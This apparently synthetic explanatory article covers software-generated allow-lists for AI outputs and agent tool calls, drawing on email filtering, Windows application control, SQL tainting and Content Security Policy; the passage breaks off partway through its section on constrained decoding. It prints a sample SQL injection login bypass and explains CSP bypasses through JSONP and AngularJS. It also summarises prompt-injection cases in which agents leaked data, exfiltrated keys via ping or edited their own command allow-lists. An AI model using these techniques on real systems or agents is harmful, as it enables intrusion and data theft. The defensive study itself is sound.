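# Dynamically generated allow-lists for the outputs of AI systems

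## What an allow-list of outputs is and when it can be trusted

An allow-list is a set of permitted items, with everything else refused. Administrators have long used such lists, often under the older name "white list", to control which programs a computer may run, which senders may reach an inbox and which machines may join a network. An allow-list of outputs applies the same rule to what a system produces, which for an AI system can mean the words a chatbot writes, the links it displays, the software packages its code installs or the commands it sends to other programs. A person writes a static list in advance, and it stays the same until somebody edits it. Software generates or changes a dynamic list while the system is in use, for a session, a task or a single response.

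Let c be the context in which the system is working, meaning who the user is, what they have asked for, and which records exist at that moment. The allow-list is a set A(c) of permitted outputs. A component called the generator builds A(c) from c, and a second component, the checker, releases a proposed output o only if o belongs to A(c). For example, an airline assistant's generator could build a different list for each passenger by looking up the bookings under their account and listing only those booking numbers. The checker would then stop any reply that quotes somebody else's booking number or one that the assistant made up.

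With a deny-list D(c), the checker blocks any output in D(c) and releases the rest. In set notation, an allow-list and a deny-list are interchangeable, because listing the permitted outputs gives the same information as listing all the others. In practice nobody can list all the others, so a deny-list releases outputs that nobody thought of, which an allow-list would block.

### Why refusal is the safer default

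The standard argument for allow-lists dates from 1975, when Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* set out eight design principles for controlling access to data on shared computers. One of them is fail-safe defaults, which they trace to a suggestion by E. Glaser in 1965. Under this principle, the system denies access by default and identifies the conditions under which it grants access. *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles* gives the example of a shop's emergency exit, which outsiders cannot use to get in and insiders may use only in an emergency.

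The designers of a large system will almost certainly overlook something. If they leave a legitimate item off an allow-list, a user gets a refusal and complains, and somebody adds the item. But a dangerous item left off a deny-list gets through, and ordinary users have no reason to look for it, so the gap can stay open until an attacker finds it.

This argument concerns entries missing from the list. An entry wrongly added to an allow-list does harm as silently as a gap in a deny-list, because the checker releases the output and nobody sees a refusal. Such entries may be rare when a careful administrator writes a short list by hand, but they become the main worry once software adds entries automatically, many times a day.

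### Items, patterns and meanings

An entry can be an exact item, such as one booking number. It can also be a pattern, such as every web address under a given domain, or a description of a meaning, such as "questions about an existing booking". More exact entries let less through by accident but need more upkeep.

*Guide to Application Whitelisting* (Sedgewick, Souppaya and Scarfone, 2015), written for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, describes this trade-off for lists of programs that a computer may run. A cryptographic hash, a fingerprint computed from a file's contents, identifies one exact file whatever its name or location, but it changes with every software update. An entry that permits a whole folder still works after updates, but it also permits any malicious file placed there, so it is only as good as the controls on who can write to the folder.

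Free text fits neither method, because people can phrase the same request in too many ways to list. *Persona Guardrail* (Pal, Maddireddy and colleagues, 2026) describes Uber's approach for its customer-facing assistants. The list consists of written descriptions of what an assistant is for, and a language model judges whether each request and reply falls under one of them. Such a checker can handle sentences no one foresaw, but it can also misjudge them, whereas a program that compares two strings of characters gives the same correct answer every time.

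### Language models, agents and prompt injection

A language model is a program trained on large amounts of text to continue a text. It writes one token at a time, where a token is a word or piece of a word. At each step, the model assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software picks one and appends it. Developers can therefore apply an allow-list during writing, using a token mask that gives forbidden next tokens zero probability, or afterwards to the finished text.

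An agent is a language model that carries out a task by calling tools in a loop. It might search a mailbox, read the result, and then decide to write a file. Each call is an output, consisting of a tool's name and the values the model fills in. A task policy is an allow-list of such calls for one user request. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, explain why a static list works badly for agents. A phone app has a developer and a mostly fixed purpose, so its permissions can be settled at installation. An agent has only a sentence from its user to define its task, so the permissions it needs depend on the request. For example, an agent asked to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site where programmers track their work, needs to open that page and write in its comment box, but needs nothing else in the user's account. If the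 user then asks for a summary of the issue, the right permissions change.

In a prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in material that a model reads, so that the model will follow them. This works because the model receives instructions and data in the same stream of text. In one attack that Christodorescu and colleagues describe, the attacker sent a message containing a hidden prompt to a user of Microsoft 365 Copilot, an office assistant. When the user asked for a summary, the prompt made Copilot search for private data and hide it in a link. Clicking the link sent the data to the attacker. Any agent that reads e-mail or web pages may at some point follow an attacker's instructions, which is why a checker should examine the model's outputs before they take effect.

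### Conditions for trusting a list that software wrote

The same danger applies to the generator, which may itself be a language model. Whether its list can be trusted depends on where the generator gets its information, who can change the list afterwards, how long entries stay on it, what form items are in when the checker compares them, and whether anything can bypass the checker.

The generator must not depend on the party that the list restrains. Sedgewick and colleagues advise building a list of permitted programs by scanning a "clean host", a computer that no end user has touched, because scanning a machine in daily use would add any malware already on it to the list. For an agent, outside text can contaminate the list in the same way. *ToolFence* (2026) generates the list with a separate model call that receives the user's request and the tool descriptions, but no untrusted content.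 *ClawGuard* (2026) similarly has a model draft the permitted domains, file paths and commands from only the operator's standing instructions and the user's message, leaving out whatever the task does not require.

A generator's trust root is the source it relies on without further proof. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) calls a value "anchored" if it comes from the user's request, a record that the operator maintains or another trusted source. Under its policy, nothing that a tool returns can establish the user's consent. These requirements alone would be too strict when a user asks the agent to act on "the most recent invoice" without giving its number, so the policy takes the selection rule from the user's request, reapplies it to the list of records, and requires the agent's choice to match the result.

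A sound trust root keeps an attacker from writing the list, but the list can still be wrong, because a user's request is often vague and the generator can misread it. *Agenra* (2026) presents a design that includes a core of checking functions with mathematical proofs, but the paper notes that the monitor cannot enforce a rule that is missing from the policy.

Nobody, especially the agent, should be able to change the list unnoticed. Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in 1975 that to find out whether a user could reach a file, one must also ask whether he could change the file's permissions, whether he could change who may change them, and so on. Amp, a coding agent from Sourcegraph, kept its list of commands that could run without approval in a settings file that it could edit. Christodorescu and colleagues report that a prompt injection could make Amp add malicious commands to that list. They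 recommend that an agent be unable to change such files and that a human approve every change.

*aiAuthZ* (2026) goes further by moving the policy to a separate computer, where the agent has no credentials to read or rewrite it. By default, the system denies any tool that the policy doesn't list and starts with an empty list of permitted web addresses. For files, though, it uses a deny-list of system folders and secret keys, so the 1975 argument only partly applies.

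Entries must also expire. Sedgewick and colleagues point out that a stale list can block legitimate software because it lacks the fingerprints of new versions, and can let programs with known flaws run because it still has the fingerprints of old ones. For an agent, the natural lifetime of a permission is the length of the task that needs it. Some designs set a fixed time instead. *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (2026) gives policies a lifetime in hours, and its policy for agent orchestration lasts 24 hours, which is long if the task takes ten minutes. But a permission that lapses too early can leave a job half done.

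The checker has to convert each item to canonical form, a single standard spelling, before comparing it with the list. If a list permits every file whose path begins with /home/ana/reports/, a checker that compares the raw characters will also release /home/ana/reports/../keys. The two dots mean "go up one folder", so that path leads to /home/ana/keys. Such a checker will wrongly refuse Example.com if the list has example.com, although both lead to the same site.

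Attackers exploit such differences. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an attack on the chatbot DeepSeek in which a text file contained a script in base64, an encoding that represents any data as ordinary characters. The model decoded the script as instructed, and the victim's browser ran it, which exposed the victim's login token. An allow-list should therefore check the output in the form that the receiving program will act on.

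Finally, the checker must check every part of every output, which Saltzer and Schroeder called complete mediation. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, required human approval for many commands that could send data to unknown addresses, but by mistake let one called "ping" run without it. Ping tests whether another machine is reachable, after first looking up the machine's name in the internet's public directory. According to Christodorescu and colleagues, an injected prompt could make the agent put secret keys into the name, so that the lookup sent them to the attacker. The list allowed the command, but nothing checked the name that followed it. *ToolFence* gives a simpler example, in which the list permits the tool "send_money" but doesn't restrict the recipient, so the model can still pay anyone.

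### Two error rates, and a worked example

A checker's false-block rate is the fraction of proper outputs it refuses. Its false-admit rate, which Pal and colleagues call the false-approved rate, is the fraction of improper outputs it releases.

In an example with invented figures, a support assistant drafts 1,000 replies, of which 980 are proper and 20 are improper, perhaps because they promise refunds the company does not give. A tight allow-list covers a few kinds of reply in narrow terms, and a loose one covers many kinds in broad terms.

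| Invented example | Tight list | Loose list |
|---|---|---|
| Improper replies released (of 20) | 1 | 8 |
| False-admit rate | 5% | 40% |
| Proper replies blocked (of 980) | 147 | 10 |
| False-block rate | 15% | about 1% |
| All wrong decisions (of 1,000) | 148 | 18 |

Neither error rate is enough by itself to compare the lists. The tight list has the lower false-admit rate and the loose list has the lower false-block rate, but a checker could get the first to zero by blocking everything or the second to zero by releasing everything. The total number of errors isn't much more useful, because improper replies are so rare that releasing everything produces only 20 wrong decisions, compared with 148 for the tight list.

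The company has to decide how many needless refusals it will accept to stop one improper reply. Moving from the loose list to the tight one stops 7 more improper replies and blocks 137 more proper ones, or roughly 20 needless refusals for each improper reply stopped. That is too many if an improper reply is an off-topic joke, but it may be acceptable if an improper reply commits the company to a large payment. The ratio also depends on how common improper replies are. If 200 of the 1,000 replies were improper and the two rates stayed the same, the tight list would stop 70 more improper replies and block about 112 more proper ones, which is fewer than two needless refusals for each improper reply stopped.

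Real measurements show the same trade-off. Pal and colleagues tested several language models as the checker for one Uber assistant. The smallest, Qwen2.5-3B, wrongly approved 11% of a general set of adversarial requests, compared with 15% for Qwen3-30B-A3B. But the smaller model approved only 49 to 67% of legitimate requests, while the larger one, which Uber deployed, approved 99 to 100%.

They also compared the two kinds of list on their own benchmark. A deny-list alone had a false-admit rate of 49.0%, mostly because it missed harmless-looking requests outside the assistant's job. An allow-list had a rate of 9.9%, which fell to 4.7% after one round of rewording, while its false-block rate stayed near 3.7%. This is the result one would expect from the 1975 argument. However, the test favours the allow-list, because the researchers labelled the messages according to the same list that the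 checker then enforced.

Both rates describe a fixed sample, but an attacker can keep trying. If each attempt had an independent 5% chance of getting past the tight list, 20 attempts would give about a 64% chance of at least one success, and an attacker who learns from each refusal may do better. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that a probabilistic checker that correctly refuses 99% of the time leaves 1% for someone to find and exploit.

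## How software came to generate its own allow-lists, 2002 to 2018

Administrators struggled to keep allow-lists up to date long before language models existed. Users gain new correspondents every week, software companies patch their programs, and web pages load code from a changing set of other sites. Editing the lists by hand was too slow, so engineers looked for ways to have software write the entries. Some programs recorded normal activity and then permitted it. Others permitted whatever came from a publisher or installer that the administrator already trusted. A more exact method tracked which characters of an output came from the program's own code. Web developers also began to label each legitimate script with a secret that changed with every page. All of these methods save labour, but each gives an attacker a way onto the list.

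### Learning from observation

An e-mail allow-list names the senders whose messages go straight to the inbox. It restricts inputs rather than outputs, but the problem of generating it is the same. In *Personal Email Networks*, Boykin and Roychowdhury (2004) generated one automatically from only the sender and recipient fields of the messages in a user's inbox.

Their program draws a network in which each address is a point and a line joins the sender of a message to everyone who received it. It then deletes the user's own addresses, and what remains falls into separate groups. To tell friends from spammers, the program measures how many of an address's contacts are also in contact with each other. An address with k neighbours has k(k − 1)/2 pairs of neighbours. If lines join E of those pairs, the clustering coefficient of the address is

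C = 2E / (k(k − 1))

An address with four neighbours has six pairs of neighbours, and if lines join four of those pairs, C is about 0.67. A group's coefficient is the average C of all its addresses that have at least two neighbours. Friends often write to each other, so a group of friends scores high. Spammers don't write to each other, and the people they write to are mostly strangers to one another, so a group formed by spam scores zero.

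In one inbox of 5,486 messages, the largest group had 3,560 addresses, all from spam, and a coefficient of zero. The next largest had 266 addresses, which were the user's real contacts, and a coefficient of 0.67. The program put groups that scored above 0.1 on the allow-list and those below 0.01 on a deny-list. It left small groups unclassified because a handful of addresses gives too little evidence.

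Boykin and Roychowdhury tested the program on the mail of two users over five to six weeks. None of the 8,619 spam messages came from a group on the allow-list, and none of the 910 legitimate messages came from a group on the deny-list. But the allow-list covered only 44% of the legitimate mail (54% for one user and 23% for the other). If the mail program had refused everything not on the allow-list, its false-block rate would have been 56%. The researchers instead passed the unclassified messages to a content filter, so mail from known contacts skipped the filter and mail from strangers could still get through. They also chose thresholds that worked on their own data, so the results may be worse for other users.

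A spammer can get onto such a list by copying the behaviour that the program looks for. If the spammer learns who the user's friends are, perhaps through a virus, and names them as fellow recipients, the spam appears to come from within the circle of friends. A stray message can also join two unrelated groups by accident, which happened once in three years of one researcher's mail. The program can separate these groups because the accidental link is usually the only one between them, but a spammer who knows the user's friends can create many links. A simpler program that lists everyone to whom the user has sent mail will add a spammer as soon as the user's out-of-office message replies to one.

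The idea lasted despite these problems. *Systems Applications of Social Networks*, a 2017 survey, treats automatic allow-lists as one of three general defences against spam, alongside detecting and tolerating it.

Administrators can also generate an allow-list by watching a program run. This list, called a program profile, covers what that one program may do, such as which files it may open and which machines it may contact. The administrator first runs the program in audit mode, in which the checker logs every action without blocking any. The log becomes the profile, and the administrator then switches the checker to enforcement mode, in which it blocks any action not in the profile.

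Audit mode serves the same purpose for lists of whole programs. Sedgewick and colleagues recommend it for the first weeks of a new allow-listing product, so that an organisation can see what the product would block without stopping anyone's work. They advise installing a software update during the trial, because a product that an administrator must switch off for every security update may be unsuitable. Many products can also run in audit and enforcement modes at once, so an administrator might block changes to operating system files while only logging changes to the registry, where Windows keeps its settings.

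If malware is active during the learning period, the log will record its behaviour as normal and a profile learned in this way will permit it from then on. A short recording also misses rare but legitimate behaviour. If a payroll program contacts the tax office only once a year, in January, a profile recorded in June would block it. Recording for longer captures more of these cases but gives malware more time to appear, so somebody should review the log before it becomes an allow-list. The same applies when developers use live traffic to refine a chat assistant's list of subjects.

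### Inheriting trust from a publisher or an installer

Observation has to start again whenever the software changes. Lists of hashes also go out of date with every patch, so an organisation may have to choose between installing security updates promptly and keeping its software working. The alternative is to list a source and permit everything that comes from it.

One such source is the publisher. Software companies can sign their files digitally, using a secret key to compute a code that anyone can check with a matching public key. AppLocker, included in Windows since Windows 7, lets administrators write rules by publisher as well as by hash or by path (the folder where the file is stored). As Sedgewick and colleagues explain, publisher rules need updating only when the organisation buys from a new company or a company changes its key. But a publisher rule permits every product the company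 has signed, including old versions with known flaws, and it can't cover the many unsigned files.

An organisation can also trust the program that installs its software. Sedgewick and colleagues describe products in which an administrator names a "trusted updater", and every file that it adds or changes goes onto the list automatically. Microsoft's *Automatically allow apps deployed by a managed installer* sets out how this works in Windows Defender Application Control, a successor to AppLocker now known as App Control for Business:

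1. An administrator designates an installer, such as the tool that the IT department uses to send software to employees' computers.
2. When the installer runs, Windows watches it and any other programs that it starts.
3. Windows attaches a tag to each file that they write to disk.
4. When a user later opens a program, Windows looks for the tag and lets the program run if it finds one, unless another rule forbids that program.

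Administrators who use Microsoft's Configuration Manager can choose a ready-made policy that, according to Microsoft, permits only Windows components, Microsoft Store applications and whatever Configuration Manager has installed. Nobody has to name each application, and the list grows whenever the IT department deploys something. Administrators can also allow other applications that a Microsoft service rates as reputable.

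The tags can let unwanted programs run and block legitimate ones. Some installers open the new application as soon as they finish. Windows treats that first run as part of the installation and tags every file the application creates, so a program it downloads then could gain permission to run. Files that arrive by any other route lack the tag, so an application may stop working after it updates itself without the installer. Windows also cannot tag software installed before the tracking began, as a reply on Microsoft's community site confirms to an administrator who complained that existing applications were being blocked.

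An administrator can fix the self-updating application by designating it as a trusted installer too. But the application can then add new programs to the list, and so can anyone who controls it. Microsoft recommends a security review first, and warns that the whole mechanism gives weaker guarantees than rules that name individual programs. Malware with administrator rights may be able to get around it, and so may malware with only an ordinary user's rights if the installer runs with those rights.

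Publisher rules have a similar weakness. A signature shows which key signed a file and that nobody has altered the file since, but it doesn't show that the file is harmless. If an attacker steals the publisher's key, or inserts code into a product before the publisher signs it, every computer that allows the publisher's software will run the result. Removing the publisher from the list would also block its legitimate products. Sedgewick and colleagues prefer to use the signature to confirm that a patch is genuine and then list the patch's hash. This lets an administrator withdraw one bad version and keep the rest, but it takes more upkeep. It also doesn't stop a malicious version when it first arrives, since the signature will still be valid.

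### Tracking where each character came from

Many programs build commands by combining their own text with text that a user typed. Trusting the program as a whole isn't enough, because part of a command can come from an attacker. *Using Positive Tainting and Syntax-Aware Evaluation to Counter SQL Injection Attacks* (Halfond, Orso and Manolios, 2006) addressed this problem for websites that query a database.

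SQL is the language in which most such websites write their queries. Suppose a login page asks for a name and a PIN. If a user enters "doe" and "123", the website inserts them into a prepared text and sends this to the database:

    SELECT acct FROM users WHERE login='doe' AND pin=123

The database returns an account only if both the name and the PIN match. Now suppose that an attacker enters admin' -- as the name and 0 as the PIN. The query becomes

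    SELECT acct FROM users WHERE login='admin' -- ' AND pin=0

In this attack, called an SQL injection, the attacker's quotation mark closes the name early. Two hyphens start a comment in SQL, so the database ignores the rest of the line, including the PIN check. The database then returns the administrator's account, which the website displays.

The older defence, called tainting, marks text from untrusted sources and follows it through the program to prevent dangerous uses. This is a form of deny-list, and it fails when developers overlook a source. At first they marked only what users typed into forms. Attackers then injected commands through cookies (small files that a website stores in the browser) and uploaded files, and later through server variables and the database.

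Positive tainting marks trusted text rather than untrusted text. In most web applications, the trusted text is what developers wrote into the program, which software can find automatically. Halfond and colleagues built a tool called WASP that marks every character of this text as trusted and preserves the marks while the program cuts and joins pieces of text. Just before a query goes to the database, WASP divides it into keywords, operators and literals (values such as names or numbers). It lets the query through only if every character outside the literals is marked as trusted.

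In the legitimate query, "doe" and "123" are unmarked, but they are literals, so the query passes. In the attacker's query, the quotation mark after "admin" and the two hyphens are unmarked operators, so WASP blocks it. WASP permits any query that the developers' own commands can form around any values. A list of these queries would be endless, so WASP checks each query individually instead of creating one.

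The researchers cite Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults to support this choice. If WASP misses a trusted source, it blocks a legitimate query, which a developer is likely to notice during testing.

Halfond and colleagues tested WASP on seven web applications, five commercial and two written by students. A master's student who knew about attack tools, but not how WASP worked, collected 30 kinds of attack from security reports and mailing lists and generated about 41,000 attempts from them. The applications' own checks stopped many of these, and WASP stopped all 12,616 that succeeded without it. The student also wrote 5,602 legitimate requests, some with SQL keywords and stray quotation marks meant to cause false alarms, and WASP blocked none of them. It slowed the applications by 6% on average and by 19%, or 16 milliseconds per request, in the worst case.

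The result is impressive, but the 12,616 attacks were based on only 30 patterns. The test also left out attacks that take several steps, such as second-order injection, in which the attacker stores harmful text in the database as ordinary data and the application later uses it to build a query. WASP would block this by default, because text from the database isn't marked as trusted.

Some applications keep pieces of their own queries in files or databases. WASP blocks these pieces too until a developer adds the file or database to the trusted sources. WASP's learning mode helps by showing the developer where in the program the blocked text originated. But once a source is trusted, anyone who can write to it can write commands. Halfond and colleagues expected developers to keep adding trusted sources during testing until the false alarms stopped, and each addition carries this risk.

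They suggest limiting what a newly trusted source may contribute. Bugzilla, a bug tracker, stores parts of its search queries in its database. A developer could permit text from the database only if it consists of conditions on two named fields, joined by AND or OR. An attacker who got text into the database could then change which bugs a search finds, but couldn't add a different command.

Even a perfect marking system controls only the commands in a query. If a user enters another customer's account number where the application expects an account number, the query has the form the developers intended, and WASP will release it. Preventing that requires a list of permitted values for each user, such as the booking numbers in the airline example.

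### Lists of permitted sites for web pages

Web pages have a problem similar to SQL injection. A page can contain scripts, small programs that the visitor's browser runs. A script on a bank's page can read what the page shows and act on the visitor's behalf. In cross-site scripting, an attacker gets their own script into the page, for example by posting it in a comment that the site displays without cleaning it. The browser runs it as if it were the bank's.

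Content Security Policy is a web standard that limits the damage when a site's developers have made such a mistake. With each page, the site's server sends an allow-list of the places from which the browser may load scripts, images and other content. The server is the generator and the browser is the checker. Experimental versions appeared in Firefox and in Chromium, the open-source basis of Google's Chrome, in 2011. A simple policy looks like this:

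    Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self' cdn.example.org; object-src 'none'

This policy tells the browser to load scripts only from the site itself and from cdn.example.org, and to load no plug-ins such as Flash, which could also run scripts. The browser also refuses inline scripts, those written directly into the page, because it can't distinguish the site's own scripts from an attacker's. A site that depends on inline scripts can switch this protection off with the keyword "unsafe-inline".

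In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, all at Google, studied how well such policies worked in practice. They searched an index of about 106 billion web addresses and found policies on roughly 1.7 million hostnames. Over a million of these hostnames belonged to five e-commerce platforms that gave the same few policies to all their shops, so the researchers counted each distinct policy once, which left 26,011.

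They then looked for ways around each policy. They first checked for three settings that made a policy useless or nearly so: permitting inline scripts, leaving plug-ins unrestricted, or permitting scripts from any site. For the fourth check, they used the search index to find sites that offered content an attacker could misuse, and tested whether the policy permitted any of them. They repeated the analysis for the policies that were in force and intended to restrict scripts, and for a "strict" group that excluded policies permitting inline scripts or scripts from any site.

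| Weakness | All policies (26,011) | Policies in force against scripts (22,425) | Strict policies (2,437) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permits inline scripts | 84.38% | 87.63% | 0% |
| Leaves plug-ins unrestricted | 12.04% | 9.40% | 14.28% |
| Permits scripts from any site | 22.12% | 21.48% | 0% |
| Permits a site with unsafe content | 75.81% | 79.17% | 41.65% |
| At least one of these | 94.72% | 94.68% | 51.05% |

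The 94.72% figure is the best known, but it mostly reflects sites that had turned off the protection against inline scripts. Many probably did so to avoid rewriting much of their code. The 41.65% in the last column is the better measure of the lists themselves. Even among developers who had avoided the obvious mistakes, about two in five had permitted a site that an attacker could use to run a script. Weichselbaum and colleagues regard this as a minimum, since they used an automated search that covered only a few kinds of unsafe content.

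To exploit such a gap in a policy, an attacker still needs a flaw in the page that lets them insert content. But Content Security Policy is meant to protect pages that have such flaws, so a policy that fails there adds nothing against cross-site scripting.

### Why a permitted site can still serve an attacker

The list permits every script from a named site, including content that the site's owner never vetted. The most common example in the study was JSONP, an older technique for fetching data from another site. The page loads the data as a script, from an address that includes the name of the function that should receive it. If the address ends in "callback=foo", the other site replies with a script that begins with "foo" and passes the data to it. An attacker who can insert a script tag (the page code that tells the browser to load a script) can point it at the same permitted site and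 put malicious code in place of "foo". The site copies that code into its reply, and the browser runs it because the reply came from a permitted site.

The researchers found JSONP on 194,908 domains. They tested for it by changing the function name in the address and checking that the change appeared at the start of the reply. In 39% of cases, an attacker could insert any code. In the rest, the attacker could only call functions that already existed on the page, which can be about as harmful.

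AngularJS, a popular library for building web pages, gives attackers another way around the allow-list. It searches a page for passages written in its own notation and executes the instructions in them. An attacker can insert such a passage, which the browser treats as plain text, along with a tag that loads AngularJS from a permitted site. The library then executes the attacker's instructions. This works even if the attacked site has never used AngularJS, as long as one of its permitted sites hosts a copy. Copies were hosted on 101,330 domains.

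Other possibilities include a file that a user has uploaded or an error message that repeats part of the web address, if the browser can read either one as a script. None of this content endangers the site that hosts it, so the site's owner has no reason to remove it. The owner may not know that other sites have put the site on their allow-lists.

Longer lists are more likely to include an unsafe site. If each site had an independent one-in-ten chance of being unsafe, a list of 12 would have a 72% chance of containing at least one. The median policy in the study permitted 12 hosts, and the longest permitted 512. The researchers could bypass 94.8% of the policies that permitted 12.

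Of the 15 hosts that developers permitted most often, 12 allowed a full bypass, and two more did if the policy also had a certain unsafe setting. Several of the 12 belonged to Google. The ten hosts most useful to attackers were enough to defeat 68% of all policies. Removing the JSONP and AngularJS content from those ten would hardly have helped, because the remaining hosts would still have defeated 66%.

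The standard lets developers permit a single folder or file on another site, but browsers stop checking the path if the request passes through a redirect, an address that sends the browser on to another one. This exception protects privacy, since a strict check could reveal where a redirect had led. However, if any permitted site offers an open redirect, an attacker can use it to reach every file on the other permitted sites.

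A list of allowed sites can take a lot of work to maintain. In February 2015 Google introduced one for Google Maps Activities, an application with 4 million monthly users. Developers had to make five major changes to the list that year as the application and its libraries changed. After these changes it had 15 long entries, and at least one of them still offered JSONP. Lists of sites to which AI assistants may link can have the same problem, because an allowed site may serve unsafe content.

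### A fresh secret for each response

Weichselbaum and colleagues proposed marking each legitimate script instead of listing sites. The standard already offered two ways to do this. One is to list the script's hash, which works well if the script never changes. Software can collect the hashes by observation. The paper describes an earlier system, by Kerschbaumer and colleagues, that identified the scripts many different users received from a site and permitted only those. But a script that the server assembles for each visitor has a different hash every time.

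The other way is a nonce, a random value that the server uses once. For each response, the server generates a new nonce, puts it in the policy and attaches it to every script tag that it means to include:

    Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-random123'; object-src 'none'

    <script nonce="random123" src="https://example.org/script.js"></script>

The browser runs only the scripts with the matching value. An attacker may insert a script tag into the page and point it at the same JSONP address as before, but can't know the value that the server will choose for the next visitor, so the browser refuses the tag. In effect, each page comes with its own list of allowed scripts, which expires as soon as the server sends the next page.

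SQLrand, a system from 2004, used a similar idea earlier. It added a secret code to every SQL keyword in a program and rejected queries whose keywords lacked it. Halfond and colleagues objected that an attacker might guess the code. A long random value that changes with every response gives an attacker very little time to guess it.

Nonces cause a problem when scripts load other scripts, as they often do. A map on a web page may start with one script that fetches several more as the visitor zooms in. The programmers of the first script usually know nothing about the page's nonce, so the browser would block the additional scripts and the map would break.

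The researchers proposed a new keyword, "strict-dynamic", which lets a script with the right nonce load further scripts from anywhere. The browser also ignores any list of permitted sites in the same policy. The researchers reasoned that a permitted script loads others because its developer chose to, and that an attacker can't use this route without first getting a script to run. The browser extends trust only to scripts that a running script creates as new elements of the page. If the script writes a tag into the page as text, the tag needs its own nonce, because the browser can't distinguish it from one that an attacker inserted.

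In Google Maps Activities, the scripts already had nonces, so the switch required no rewriting. The developers removed the 15 entries, and by October 2016, when the paper appeared, they had not needed to change the policy again. By then, Google had introduced the same kind of policy in Google Photos, Cloud Console and other products.

A company that still wants to control which sites its developers load scripts from can send two policies with one page. The browser enforces both, so a script needs a valid nonce and must also come from a permitted site. Listing the nonce and the sites in a single policy would not work, because a script would then need to match only one of them.

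### How nonces fail, and who uses them

A nonce is useful only while the attacker doesn't have it. Many websites use caches, which store a copy of a page and send it to later visitors. If that copy includes the nonce, every visitor receives the same value, and an attacker can read it and attach it to a malicious script. The policy still looks the same as a sound one, and CentralCSP, which scans websites for their policies, says its scans can't tell whether a site generates a new nonce for each response.

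The server can also give a valid nonce to a script that contains an attacker's code. Suppose a search page carelessly inserts the visitor's search term into one of its own scripts. An attacker can write a search term that contains code and send the victim a link to the results. When the victim opens the link, the code runs because it is inside a script with a valid nonce.

"Strict-dynamic" adds a risk of passing trust on too far. A permitted script might take the address of the next script from the page's own web address, which an attacker can change by sending somebody a link. The browser then runs whatever script the attacker chose. A list of sites would at least have limited the attacker to the sites on it. The same kind of error occurs when the Windows installer passes its trust to everything a new application creates in its first run.

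Weichselbaum and colleagues accepted this drawback. After examining hundreds of cross-site scripting flaws recorded inside Google, they expected nonces to stop a large majority. They did not claim that nonces would stop attacks that need no script, such as inserting a fake login form that sends the visitor's password elsewhere.

Nonces have become much more common since 2016, but "strict-dynamic" has not. In the 2016 study, fewer than 1% of policies used a nonce. Report URI (2026), a company that sells monitoring for these policies, examined 170,057 of them in June 2026 and found a nonce in 24.7% and "strict-dynamic" in 1.6%. The two studies are not strictly comparable, because the 2016 study counted each distinct policy once. In the 2026 study, a single hosting company that adds nonces for all its customers could raise the nonce figure considerably.

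Report URI also found "unsafe-inline" in 46.8% of policies. Some of those may be sound, since browsers that support nonces ignore the keyword when the policy also has a nonce. At least 28.5% of all the policies have neither "unsafe-inline" nor a nonce, and the share is higher if some policies have both. Policies with neither may rely on the lists of sites that the 2016 study found weak, or may not restrict scripts at all. Most sites still have no policy. CentralCSP found one on 22.0% of the domains it scanned, close to the 21.9% of mobile home pages that it quotes from the 2025 Web Almanac, an annual survey of the web.

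Evidence that nonces reduce successful attacks is harder to find. Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting* cites Google's payments to outsiders who report security flaws. Cross-site scripting accounted for 30% of these payments in 2018 and 4.1% in 2023, after Google had moved its products to stricter policies. The drop is large, but Report URI has a product to sell, and Google may have introduced other defences in the same years. The share may also have fallen because Google paid more for other kinds of flaw.

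## Restricting a language model's words as it writes, 2016 to 2026

WASP and Content Security Policy check text after a program has produced it. A token mask removes forbidden tokens before a language model chooses each token. The model then can't write anything outside the list, so there is no need to discard a finished answer and request another. Google used an early form of this method in 2016 to suggest replies to e-mails.

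### A prepared set of e-mail replies

Smart Reply, a feature of Google's Inbox app, offered up to three short answers that a user could send with one tap. Kannan, Kurach and colleagues (2016), in *Smart Reply*, describe a neural network that learned from real e-mails and their replies how likely each reply was. Real replies include "thanks hon!", "your the best!" and "Leave me alone", which Google did not want to suggest to strangers. Banning certain words would not have solved the problem, since every word in "Leave me alone" is harmless. The researchers instead restricted the system to a prepared set of replies, which software mostly built:

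1. The software collected the most frequent sentences from users' e-mails, with identifying details removed. This gave a few million.
2. It reduced each sentence to its main words, so that "Thanks for your kind update" and "Thanks for the status update" counted as the same message.
3. It grouped the sentences by meaning. The researchers defined 100 groups, such as "thanks" and "sounds good", with a few examples of each. The software extended these labels to sentences that shared words and phrases with the examples. It then tried 100 unlabelled sentences as possible new groups, and repeated this until it found no more.
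4. Human raters looked at the highest-scoring sentences in each group and judged whether they belonged there.

The raters' question was about meaning, so a rude sentence could pass if it was in the right group.

Scoring every reply in the set for every e-mail would have taken too long. The software therefore stored the set as a prefix tree, in which replies with the same beginning share a branch, as "I can do Tuesday" and "I can do Wednesday" do until the last word. It moved through the tree one word at a time and kept only the most probable beginnings, a method called beam search. The search time depended on the length of the replies and the number of beginnings kept, but not on the size of the set. The search found the same best reply as scoring the full set in 93% of cases when it kept 16 beginnings, and in 99% when it kept 128.

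The permitted set could also change with the e-mail. The network tended to suggest positive replies, so if its top suggestions included a positive reply but no negative one, the software searched again among only negative replies and put the best one in third place. For "Can you join tomorrow's meeting?", it suggested "Sure, I'll be there", "Yes, I can" and "Sorry, I won't be able to make it tomorrow".

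Users used Smart Reply for 10% of the replies they sent from Inbox on mobile phones. In a sample of 10 million short replies, more than 40% appeared only once, so no prepared set could cover everything people write. A reply missing from Smart Reply's set did little harm, because the user could type it. *Efficient Natural Language Response Suggestion for Smart Reply* (2017) describes a later version that still chose from a fixed set.

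### A tree of permitted names

*Autoregressive Entity Retrieval* (De Cao, Izacard and colleagues, 2020) introduced GENRE, a system that reads a passage with a marked name and writes the title of the Wikipedia article about that person, place or thing. For "Leonardo" in a sentence about the Mona Lisa, it should write "Leonardo da Vinci". An unrestricted model may write a title that doesn't exist, so GENRE uses a prefix tree to permit only the roughly 6 million real titles.

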